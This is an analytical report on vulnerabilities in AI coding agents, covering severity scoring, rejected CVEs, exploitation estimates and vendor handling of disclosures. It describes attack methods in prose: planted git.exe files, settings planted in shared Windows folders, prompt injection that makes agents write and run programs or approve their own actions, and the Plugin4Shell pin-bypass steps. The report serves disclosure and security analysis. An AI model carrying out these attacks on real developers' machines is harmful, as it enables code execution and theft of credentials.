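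Differences in judgment alone gave the Zsh flaw three scores under version 3.1 that range from medium to critical. GitLab gave the same answers as GitHub. Endor Labs changed only the answer on user interaction, to "none". NVD also chose "none", but said an attacker would need low privileges and counted harm only to integrity, because the flaw let the agent write files. NVD's answers follow the public description closely but may underrate the flaw, because an attacker who can write to a shell startup file can run code later, as Chester did with the `sed` flaw.

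The symlink flaw has the opposite pattern, and most of its gap comes from the version. According to GCVE's *CVE-2025-59829* (2025), GitHub expected a low loss of both confidentiality and integrity, while NVD expected a high loss of confidentiality and no loss of integrity. NVD's rating seems closer to the actual danger, since people usually deny an agent access to a file because it holds secrets. But the flaw allowed "access" in general, which could include writing to the file.

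A company that rushes out patches only for flaws rated critical would do so for two of these four using NVD's scores and for none using GitHub's. For newer flaws, it might not have two scores to choose between, because NIST no longer routinely adds one when the original record already has a score.

OpenAI's record for the PowerShell flaw has no score, so databases repeat CISA's 8.8. The record lists several conditions the attack depends on, but none of them affects CISA's score. The mismatch between score and description is worse for the filter flaw in Codex. On one OpenCVE page, its 9.8 score is based on a network attack with no user interaction, while an AI-generated summary describes it as "not a passive or remote attack".

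### What a base score leaves out

CVSS doesn't measure how often a model obeys an attacker's instructions. An attack that works almost every time can get the same score as one the model may usually refuse, like Fogel's `git show` attack. One defence of leaving this out is that a base score should stay constant over time, and a success rate would change with every new model. Attackers can also retry easily, so a flaw that works one time in ten is still serious.

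A flaw's severity also depends on the user's approval mode. A flaw that skips the approval prompt adds little danger for someone who has already turned prompts off, but it could be the main danger for someone who reads each one. The harm also depends on what the agent can reach. The same attack may destroy a disposable test machine in one setup and steal the keys to a company's cloud servers in another.

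CVSS lets users adjust scores for their own situation with environmental metrics. In version 4.0, these default to the worst case until somebody fills them in (FIRST, 2023). Under version 3.1, a company that uses Codex only on test machines that hold nothing valuable can set the importance of confidentiality, integrity and availability to low. This halves their weights and reduces the PowerShell flaw's score from 8.8 to 6.9. If all the company's Macs have a sandbox that blocks the change to Codex's settings, it can set the impact to none, which reduces the score to 0.

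The adjustment is less effective at raising a score than at lowering one. A company whose developers hold production keys could mark all three as highly important, but the score would stay at 8.8 because the formula caps the impact and the flaw is already near the cap. Developers who work alone are also unlikely to do the calculation.

The attack requirements question in version 4.0 helps with a different problem. GitHub's answers for CVE-2025-66032 and CVE-2026-24053 differ only on that question, and the flaws score 8.7 and 7.7 respectively. The PowerShell flaw in Codex clearly has such requirements, and opening a project is passive interaction, so it would score 7.7, a point below CISA's score. But the only possible answers are "present" and "none", so a flaw that needs several unlikely conditions loses the same point as one that needs Zsh, which most Mac users already have.

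Another possible remedy is to publish more information beside the score. SecurityWeek reported that version 3.1 came with a framework for adding industry-specific metrics while keeping the official ones. It also reported that healthcare and industrial specialists had complained that CVSS could give misleading scores in their fields. Version 4.0 has supplemental metrics, which also don't change the score.

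An extension for coding agents could record which models followed the attacker's instructions in testing and how often, which approval modes were vulnerable, and whether the sandbox stopped the attack. For the PowerShell flaw, a Mac user would learn from the entry that the default sandbox can block the attack, and a Windows user would learn that OpenAI gives no such assurance. Either user would find this more useful than a choice between scores of 7.7 and 8.8. Vendors would have to measure and publish how often attacks succeed, which could embarrass them, and repeat the tests as models change.

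### Three Claude Code CVEs that VulnCheck rejected

The organization that assigns a CVE number can also withdraw it. VulnCheck published CVE-2026-35020, CVE-2026-35021 and CVE-2026-35022 on April 6, 2026, and rejected all three on May 29. The last is the login-helper flaw that VulnCheck had rated critical. CVEFeed's *CVE-2026-35022* (2026) shows that the record gained a "disputed" tag a week after publication.

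| CVE | Reported weakness | Scores before rejection (3.x and 4.0) | Reason for rejection |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-35020 | A value in the `TERMINAL` variable could run a command | 8.4 and 8.6 | The attacker must already control the user's environment variables |
| CVE-2026-35021 | A crafted file path could run a command when Claude Code opened an editor | 7.8 and 8.4 | Normal use cannot reach the code |
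| CVE-2026-35022 | A setting for a login helper could run any command | 9.8 and 9.3 | Anthropic documents the behaviour and warns about it |

The rejection of CVE-2026-35020 is the most convincing. According to GCVE's *CVE-2026-35020* (2026), an attacker who controls the environment variables can already run code. This fits the CVSS rule that scorers should count only what the attacker gains from the flaw. BeyondMachines' *Anthropic Claude Code Leak Reveals Critical Command Injection Vulnerabilities*, written before the rejection, suggested that an attacker could set the variable through a `.env` file. A project's `.env` file did cause a flaw in Codex, but BeyondMachines did not explain how such a file would change Claude Code's environment.

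For CVE-2026-35021, VulnCheck's *Anthropic Claude Code & Agent SDK OS Command Injection via promptEditor.ts* describes how the shell still runs certain expressions inside double quotation marks. The rejection relies on a separate claim, repeated in CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-35021* (2026), that normal use of Claude Code can't trigger the affected code, and doesn't dispute how the shell behaves. Unsafe code that attackers can't reach is still worth fixing, but it poses no immediate risk.

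The severity of CVE-2026-35022 is harder to settle. BeyondMachines was mainly concerned with automated build systems, where Claude Code runs non-interactively and shows no trust dialog. An attacker could submit a pull request that changed the project's login-helper setting to run the attacker's own command. If the build system then ran Claude Code on the pull request, that command could steal the system's cloud keys.

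GCVE's *CVE-2026-35022* (2026) gives VulnCheck's answer that Claude Code behaves as described, because its help text warns people to use this mode only in trusted folders. Running a stranger's pull request with access to secrets is dangerous with many build tools, and those tools don't normally get a CVE for it.

But even with a warning, an attacker in this scenario can still use a pull request to get the company's keys. The person who set up the build system may never have read the help text. Anthropic once published a high-severity advisory because its trust dialog was not clear enough, so an inadequate warning can count as a flaw. The case for rejection is reasonable, but it depends on making the build system's owner responsible for keeping untrusted projects out. Novee later demonstrated secrets leaking from build systems, which suggests that some owners fail to do this.

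Other databases still list the old scores. OSV's *CVE-2026-35022* (2026), last modified in July, rates the flaw 9.3, and INCIBE's *CVE-2026-35021* (2026) shows both old scores beside the rejection notice. A security scanner that copies these scores could raise an alarm about a rejected record. Without the three rejected records, the rough minimum of 102 disclosed flaws across the field drops to 99, before adding any from IDEsaster and Manifold Security.

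### Valid reports that vendors rated lower

Vendors also judge severity when they decide how to treat a report, and they don't have to use CVSS. Google accepted Pillar Security's two Antigravity reports as valid but downgraded both because it considered the flaws difficult to exploit. In an explanation that Cohen and colleagues reproduce, Google said the Seatbelt attack would require social engineering or a user who trusted a project containing an indirect prompt injection.

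Google has a point about the individual attacks. One required non-default settings, and the other required the user to reopen the project. Someone deciding which reports to fix first could reasonably rank both below a flaw that works on default settings with no further action by the user.

Pillar responds that coding agents routinely read untrusted text. Other vendors' high-severity flaws also start from a trusted project containing planted text. Even if the difficulty Google cites counts as high attack complexity, an attack that requires user interaction and has a high impact on confidentiality, integrity and availability scores 7.0 locally or 7.5 over a network, both in the high range.

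The conditions required for the Seatbelt attack are a better reason than the general objection about trust to give it a lower priority. The task-file attack deserved more weight because it got past Secure Mode.

OpenAI and the Zero Day Initiative disagreed more sharply about a Codex sandbox escape. The Zero Day Initiative's *(0Day) OpenAI Codex Sandbox Escape Vulnerability* (2026) describes how malicious JavaScript in a project could escape Codex's JavaScript environment and run code as the user. The Zero Day Initiative rated the flaw 8.6. According to OffSeq's *ZDI-26-305*, OpenAI reproduced the behaviour but considered it outside its bug bounty programme because the affected component was not part of the default product.

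Whether a feature is on by default should affect how many people are at risk, but it doesn't change what happens to someone who uses it. A CVSS base score describes that person's situation. OpenAI and the Zero Day Initiative could therefore both be right about the facts and still disagree about whether the flaw needed urgent attention.

### Evidence of real attacks

A flaw can have a high severity score even if nobody has exploited it. The Exploit Prediction Scoring System (EPSS), another FIRST project, estimates the probability that attackers will try to exploit a CVE in the next 30 days. CISA separately marks the state of exploitation on many CVE records as "none" (no known attacks and no public demonstration), "PoC" (a proof of concept is public), or "active" (attacks have happened).

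| Flaw | EPSS estimate | CISA's assessment |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot, CVE-2025-53773 | 12.09% (June 2026) | None |
| Codex, CVE-2025-61260 | 6.32% (undated) | PoC |
| Claude Code, CVE-2025-66032 | 0.64% (July 2026) | PoC |
| Claude Code, CVE-2026-24053 | 0.46% (July 2026) | None |
| Claude Code, CVE-2025-59829 | 0.45% (October 2026) | None |
| Claude Code, CVE-2026-25725 | 0.42% (July 2026) | None |
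| Codex, CVE-2026-19591 | Under 1% | None |

EPSS estimates of the chance of exploitation bear little relation to severity. The sandbox escape that NVD scored 10.0 has the lowest listed percentage, below even the symlink flaw that GitHub scored 2.3. CVE-2026-35022 still had an EPSS estimate of 0.6% on the day VulnCheck rejected it.

STAR Labs' *GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio* (2025) lists an EPSS estimate of 2.6% for the Copilot flaw, but by June 2026 the estimate had reached 12.09%, higher than for about 94% of all CVEs. CVELogic's *CVE-2025-53773* (2025) reports that it rose by 5.49 percentage points in one day and interprets this as growing interest from attackers. CVELogic doesn't report an actual attack, though, and because the estimate comes from a statistical model, new data or a change in the model could also have caused the jump.

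The Codex flaw involving a project's `.env` file also ranks high. Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Injection Affecting @openai/codex package, versions <0.23.0* (2026) puts it in the 93rd percentile. GCVE's *CVE-2025-61260* shows that CISA considered attacks on it automatable, unlike attacks on the other flaws in the table. That assessment makes sense because the attacker's settings load when the developer starts Codex, without a model having to follow the attacker's instructions.

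CISA's assessments can be out of date. It rated the Copilot flaw "none" for exploitation on August 13, 2025, hours after the CVE record gained a link to Rehberger's working demonstration. NVD tags that link as an exploit. MITRE's copy of the record, updated in February 2026, still has CISA's original rating, and Microsoft's data still lists exploit code as unproven. Microsoft had judged exploitation "less likely" when it released the fix.

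CISA has marked none of the seven flaws "active". Its catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities does not include the PowerShell or filter flaws in Codex, according to OpenCVE, and RadicalNotion.AI found no match there for any of the Claude Code CVEs it lists. So there is no public confirmation that attackers have used these flaws. This is limited evidence of safety, because EPSS and CISA's catalogue cover only flaws with a CVE number, which leaves out most of the reports in "Bad Vibes". An attack through an agent may also be hard to recognise afterwards, because it would appear in the logs as the developer's own tool running a command under the developer's own account.

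The Miasma worm showed that attackers are already interested in the same configuration files. It used features that worked as designed, so patching the flaws in the table would not have protected its victims.

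## How did vendors handle reports, patches and public notices?

In early 2026, three researchers at the security company Cymulate reported the same Windows flaw to Anthropic, Cursor, OpenAI and Google. By mid-June, only Anthropic had fixed it. The vendors' responses can be compared unusually directly because all four had to judge the same technical argument from the same people.

Kalendarov, Zamir and Beber (2026) explain in *CVE-2026-35603* that any Windows user can create folders in `C:\ProgramData`, which holds settings that apply to everyone who uses the computer. Each of the four products read settings from its own folder there, but none created or protected that folder during installation. Someone with an ordinary account could therefore create it and add a settings file containing a command. The product would run the command with the permissions of the next person who used it, even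 if that person was an administrator. In Codex, the planted file could also turn off the sandbox and every approval prompt.

Anthropic received the report on January 5. It moved the settings to a folder that only administrators can change, and emailed affected companies beforehand because the move could disrupt their setups. OpenAI's bug bounty programme reproduced the flaw but marked it "Unresolved" after more than two months without meaningful progress. Google replied that it would update its documentation. Cursor had not given a verdict after five months.

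The attacker needs an account on the victim's computer, so a vendor could reasonably give this flaw a lower priority than one that works through a web page. But a lower priority doesn't explain five months without an answer, and a documentation update protects only the administrators who read it.

### Where reports go and what vendors turn away

OpenAI aims to acknowledge reports within three business days and asks researchers to keep the details private while it works on a fix. Its policy on CVE numbers excludes jailbreaks, misconfigurations, extra layers of defence and "informational findings", and generally excludes flaws on its own servers. OpenAI has a lot of discretion over what counts as "informational", and it used that discretion for the Docker sandbox report.

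Cursor answers an emailed report by inviting the researcher to a private programme on HackerOne. Microsoft's security team passed one report about Copilot's command-line tool to GitHub, which has its own bounty programme.

The table gives a quick and a slow case for each vendor. These are individual cases with known dates, so they don't show a vendor's average.

| Vendor | Where reports went | A reason for declining a report | Quick case | Slow case |
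|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | HackerOne | The user had trusted the folder | Name lookups: 11 days | Built-in browser: no confirmed fix after three months |
| OpenAI | Bugcrowd | The attacker must already have access | `.env` settings: 13 days | Shared settings folder: no fix after four months |
| Microsoft and GitHub | Microsoft or GitHub | The user had trusted the folder | Copilot auto-approve: six weeks | Copilot CLI, planted `git.exe`: no fix after almost four months |
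| Google | Google's reward programmes | The documentation covers the risk | Antigravity file search: seven weeks | Gemini CLI, planted `git.exe`: no fix after five months |
| Cursor | Email, then HackerOne | The project must already be malicious | Worktree setup: three days | Planted `git.exe`: about seven months |

### Seven months over a planted Git program

Cursor runs Git when a developer opens a project. On Windows, it looked for Git in several places, including the project folder, so a malicious project could supply its own `git.exe`. Cursor ran that file without prompting the user and kept running it while the project stayed open. Mindgard, an AI security company, demonstrated the flaw with a renamed copy of the Windows calculator.

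Mindgard's founder, Peter Garraghan, told The Hacker News that Cursor probably called `git` without a full path. Windows then searches the current folder before the usual program folders. Mindgard had not verified this explanation.

Mindgard's *Cursor 0day* gives the following timeline:

- **December 15, 2025:** Mindgard finds the flaw and emails Cursor's security address.
- **January 15, 2026:** Two days after Mindgard asks for a contact on LinkedIn, Cursor's security chief explains that an automatic invitation to HackerOne failed. Mindgard submits the report there.
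- **January 16:** The programme closes the report as informative and out of scope. Mindgard objects, and HackerOne reproduces the attack and reopens the report.
- **February 16 to April 1:** Mindgard asks for news three times and writes directly to the security chief. Cursor doesn't reply.
- **June 1:** Mindgard tells HackerOne that it intends to publish.
- **July 14:** Mindgard publishes the full details.

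Cursor was answering other researchers during this time. It published an advisory for CVE-2026-26268, the Git hooks flaw, three days before Mindgard's February request.

In *Addressing the recent Mindgard report* (2026), Cursor defended the decision to exclude the flaw from the bounty programme. It argued that customers choose which projects to open and that it gives them the workspace trust feature to manage the risk. It also admitted that it had been slow to reply to the researcher.

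Cursor's defence is weak because workspace trust is off by default in its editor. Cursor had also accepted the Git hooks flaw, which could start from a malicious project too. Cursor had a point about the conditions, since the attack worked only on Windows and needed a file named exactly `git.exe` at the top of the project. But an attacker can easily meet them, because an ordinary clone copies the file.

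Cursor has fixed the flaw. It said in an August update to its statement that the editor now finds Git on its own, runs it by its full path, and rejects any copy in the open folder or the folders above it. Cursor recommends version 3.13.25 or later.

The date of the fix is less clear. In the Cursor forum thread *Request for official public advisory or changelog entry*, a customer cited press reports in which Cursor said it had addressed the issue on July 13, the day before Mindgard published. Cursor's July 15 statement did not mention a fix. Mindgard had last tested the flaw on April 30, in version 3.2.16, so it could not have known whether a July release was still vulnerable.

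The customer's security team could find no official notice, so it had stopped the company's developers from using Cursor. The customer's own tests suggested the attack no longer worked, but the team wanted confirmation from Cursor. Cursor eventually confirmed the change in the thread and called the criticism of its communication "fair feedback".

Another company, VulnCheck, assigned CVE-2026-63093 on July 17, with a score of 8.7, in *Cursor for Windows 3.2.16 RCE via Malicious git.exe in Workspace* (2026). The record lists only version 3.2.16 as affected and gives no fixed version, so a scanner that relies on it could miss other vulnerable versions.

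### How other vendors treated the same weakness

*When AI Tools Become the Backdoor* (Kalendarov, Zamir and Beber, 2026) reports that Copilot CLI, Gemini CLI and the Codex desktop app also ran a planted `git.exe`. Copilot CLI did so before asking whether the user trusted the folder. GitHub paid a bounty for the Copilot CLI report but downgraded it to low severity and gave no date for a fix. GitHub's policy is not to disclose low-severity reports, so users would not have learned of the flaw from the company. Google accepted the Gemini CLI report as valid. None of the three tools had a fix as of June 4.

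OpenAI closed the Codex report as "Not Applicable" after eight days, reasoning that an attacker who can replace `git.exe` remotely already has access to the system. But in the reported attack, the attacker puts another copy of `git.exe` in a project and waits for the developer to open the project, without replacing the installed copy.

OpenAI later assigned a CVE number to a very similar attack, the Git hooks flaw in the Codex desktop app (CVE-2026-19590). In both attacks, the attacker's program runs outside the sandbox without approval. The hooks attack is harder to deliver, because an ordinary clone leaves out the dangerous setting but keeps a planted `git.exe`. If OpenAI considered the hooks flaw a vulnerability, its reason for rejecting the `git.exe` report is unsound.

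Cursor's command-line agent had a version of the flaw that could be exploited even if the project started out harmless. Planted text could make the agent write a program called `npx.exe` into the project without approval, and the agent ran it after a restart. Cursor closed the report as informative eight days later, saying that findings that require a malicious program "lack an attack vector". Cursor did not address the half of the report that explained how the agent itself could create the program.

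Vendors and researchers can also disagree about whether an attack works at all. OpenAI closed another report about Codex CLI as "Not Reproducible" in April 2026, according to Cymulate, which had reproduced the attack on several Windows machines.

### A fix in three days and no advisory

Cursor responded much faster to a flaw in its command-line agent's worktree feature. When a developer started the agent in a new worktree, the agent ran setup commands from a project file before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. The commands ran outside the sandbox even if the developer had turned it on.

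Manifold Security reported this on July 20, 2026, and Cursor released a fix on July 23. Six days later, Cursor closed the report as informative, a label for findings with no security impact. Mascellino reports that Cursor did so because the victim has to open a malicious project and Manifold had not shown a way around workspace trust.

Manifold replied that developers use Cursor precisely to open projects. Cursor's decision on Manifold's report is hard to reconcile with the high-severity advisory it published in 2025 for CVE-2025-64109, a flaw that let another file in the same folder start an attacker's program.

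Cursor could have told users about the fix without paying for the report. It published no advisory and left the fixed build out of its July changelog, so developers who update by hand had no official reason to install it quickly. The fix was also incomplete, because although the update moved the setup commands behind the trust prompt, they still ran outside the sandbox when Manifold published its findings on August 10.

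### Plugin4Shell: four agents and two fixes

Coding agents can install plugins (packages of extra instructions and tools) from catalogues called marketplaces. A marketplace can "pin" a plugin to one reviewed version by recording its commit hash, a 40-character string that identifies a snapshot of the code. If the plugin's owner later changes the code, the agent should still install the reviewed version.

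On September 17, 2026, AIR's *Plugin4Shell* described a way to bypass the pin in Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI. The attacker must control the repository that holds the plugin, for example by stealing the owner's account.

1. The attacker creates a branch whose name is the pinned hash, puts malicious code on it, and makes it the repository's default branch.
2. The agent asks Git for the pinned hash.
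3. Git finds both a branch and a snapshot with that name, and chooses the branch.
4. The agent installs the malicious code and reports that it installed the pinned version.

Gemini CLI fetched the right snapshot but then referred to it as `FETCH_HEAD`, Git's temporary name for whatever was just downloaded. An attacker could take over that name by creating a branch called `FETCH_HEAD`. *Plugin4Shell* (Constantin, 2026) describes a one-line fix that compares the installed snapshot with the pin and stops if they differ.

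| Agent | Response after AIR's report in June | Status in late September |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Anthropic confirmed a fix on June 17 | Fixed in 2.1.179 |
| Codex | AIR verified OpenAI's fix on August 12 | Fixed in 0.146.0 |
| GitHub Copilot | No fix reported | No fix found |
| Gemini CLI | Google said on August 4 that it would not fix a product it was retiring | No fix planned |

Digital Matters' *Plugin4Shell* (2026) found no CVE number or advisory on the vendors' pages on September 27. Codex's changelog mentioned the check of plugin hashes, but Claude Code's release notes did not. GitHub's documentation still described a pinned plugin as safe from changes to branches.

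AIR calls the flaw "zero-click" because a victim only needs to have a plugin from a trusted marketplace. It estimates that millions of agents were vulnerable, but attackers could probably reach fewer. AIR says GitHub rejects branch names that look like hashes, so the attack on the first three agents needed a plugin hosted elsewhere. AIR sells a competing marketplace, which gives it a reason to stress the danger.

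Google's refusal makes more sense for individual users, whom it had already moved to another product, than for companies that still have licensed access to Gemini CLI. Those companies can limit who adds plugin sources and check who owns each repository.

### What the public records explain

Microsoft's one-sentence record for CVE-2025-53773, the flaw that let Copilot approve its own actions, doesn't mention the settings file or the planted text, and MITRE's copy shows that it credits no researcher. A short notice can keep useful details from attackers while people update, but Rehberger's full demonstration was public within hours, so the brevity mostly hurt readers who relied on the official record.

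OpenAI, which acts as its own CNA, writes much fuller records. In its record for CVE-2026-19591, the PowerShell flaw in Codex, it explains what the check misread and each condition the attack needs. It lists affected and fixed versions separately for the command-line tool and three desktop packages. According to MITRE's copy of the record, OpenAI also suggests a temporary precaution, names five researchers and links to the code change.

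OpenAI's practice doesn't fully match its policy. OpenAI promises in the policy that public records will link to its advisories, but the only link in this record leads to the code. An earlier record from OpenAI (2026) covers CVE-2026-14898, a leak through images in the Codex app for macOS. OpenAI published that record within six minutes of reserving the number, so it evidently doesn't always reserve numbers early.

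| Vendor | Who assigned the CVE | What the notice explained | How the fix reached users |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | GitHub until Anthropic became a CNA in July 2026 | Versions and effects, but often little about the cause | Automatic updates by default |
| OpenAI | OpenAI for the 2026 flaws above | Cause, conditions, versions and precautions | New releases, which its records tell users to install |
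| Microsoft | Microsoft | One sentence for CVE-2025-53773 | A Visual Studio update |
| Google | None for the Gemini CLI flaws above | No advisory in those cases | No fix in those cases |
| Cursor | Usually GitHub, but VulnCheck for `git.exe` | From full advisories to nothing | New releases |

### From the Pwn2Own stage to a public advisory

Public explanations of the Codex flaws demonstrated at Pwn2Own Berlin in May 2026 took months to appear, even though everyone cooperated. The Zero Day Initiative, which runs the contest, says it reported the flaws to OpenAI on June 2. OpenAI reserved CVE numbers for at least two of them on August 12 and published all three records on September 1. The Zero Day Initiative released its advisories on September 10, 100 days after the report date.

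The fixes seem to have come much sooner. The first safe version of the Codex app for macOS is 26.519.22136, whose number probably stands for May 19, 2026. If so, OpenAI released a fix within days of the contest, two weeks before the formal report date. Users who updated promptly were protected, but no one explained why the update mattered for more than three months, so users who put it off had no way of knowing the risk.

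This fits the pattern Ashkenazi and Tsukerman found among large vendors, in which fixes are quick but CVE numbers take much longer. In an extreme case, the CVE record for the Codex flaw involving a project's `.env` file came out almost eight months after the fix.

A late CVE record matters most to companies, because their security teams often use software that compares installed versions with these records. That software can't warn them about a flaw that has no record.

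### What automatic updates achieve

Claude Code normally updates itself, and Anthropic often notes in its advisories that users on standard automatic updates already have the fix. Automatic updates make a late notice less dangerous. Anthropic released its Plugin4Shell fix three months before AIR published the flaw, so most users with automatic updates were probably protected before attackers could read about it. Anthropic can also force an update, as it did after the `echo` flaw.

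Automatic updates don't reach people who have turned them off or companies that approve each version before installing it. They also may not reach build systems that start from a saved copy of Claude Code. These users depend on release notes. The notes for version 2.1.179 described connection problems, scrolling and plugin loading speed but not the security fix, so a cautious company could have read them and decided to delay the update.

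An update may also need a restart, as with Claude Code's editor extensions in 2025, or work by an administrator. When Anthropic moved the shared Windows settings, companies had to move their own files too, so Anthropic's emails were useful. The advisories don't give the number of people still running old versions.

Flaws on a vendor's own servers are simpler. When GitHub fixed CamoLeak, no user had to install anything.

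### What researchers are paid

Ashkenazi and Tsukerman received around $50,000 in bounties for the 48 reports they sent to Anthropic, Google, OpenAI and Cursor, an average of about $1,000 per report, including any that earned nothing. At Pwn2Own, ten working attacks on coding agents earned $205,000, or about $20,000 each.

The comparison is rough, because contest entrants had to build a complete attack that worked on stage, while many of the other reports covered a single failed check. Still, the gap gives researchers a reason to save their best findings for a contest, so a vendor may learn of a flaw months later than it would have through its own programme.

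GitHub's handling of the Copilot CLI report shows that paying for a report doesn't guarantee a fix or a public notice. Researchers who want users to know about a flaw may have to publish it themselves.

### Should researchers publish a flaw before there is a fix?

The case for delaying publication is strongest when an attack is easy to copy. Anyone who read Mindgard's post could rename a malicious program `git.exe` and add it to a project. Most users had no simple defence. Mindgard suggested that companies block programs from running in project folders and that individuals open unfamiliar projects in a virtual machine, which few people will do every day. The post also led at least one company to stop using Cursor while it looked for an official answer.

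Mindgard argues that keeping the flaw secret no longer protected users, because Cursor kept releasing vulnerable versions and would not say whether it was working on a fix. Secrecy also had limited value because an attacker could easily have thought of trying the same attack on Cursor. Cymulate had published the same weakness in other coding agents in June, and a 2020 vulnerability in another Git tool had also involved a planted `git.exe`.

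As a compromise, researchers sometimes announce a flaw but withhold the details. That would hardly have worked for `git.exe`, because any useful warning would have to name the file to look for, and the name would reveal the attack.

A deadline announced in advance is usually better. Many researchers give vendors 90 days, with more time if a fix is close. Under that rule, Mindgard would have published in mid-March instead of July. Cursor reportedly fixed the flaw on July 13, six weeks after Mindgard announced its plan to publish and one day before Mindgard published. Months of earlier requests had produced no visible result, though the timing doesn't prove that the deadline caused the fix.

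AIR waited about three months before publishing Plugin4Shell. Waiting longer would not have helped Gemini CLI users, because Google had already refused to fix the flaw. The timing is harder to judge for Copilot, since a few more weeks might have produced a patch. But Copilot users could already reduce the risk by restricting plugin sources, and they needed to know that pinning a plugin would not protect them by itself.

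A researcher can also get a flaw into the public databases without the vendor's help, as happened with `git.exe`. A CVE Program pilot sets rules for AI companies that find flaws in other people's software. If the supplier isn't a CNA and no other CNA has acted, the company that found the flaw may assign a CVE number and publish a record after 72 hours. That would shorten the wait for a number, but most vendors need far longer than that to release a fix, so companies in the pilot will face the same choice about when to publish.
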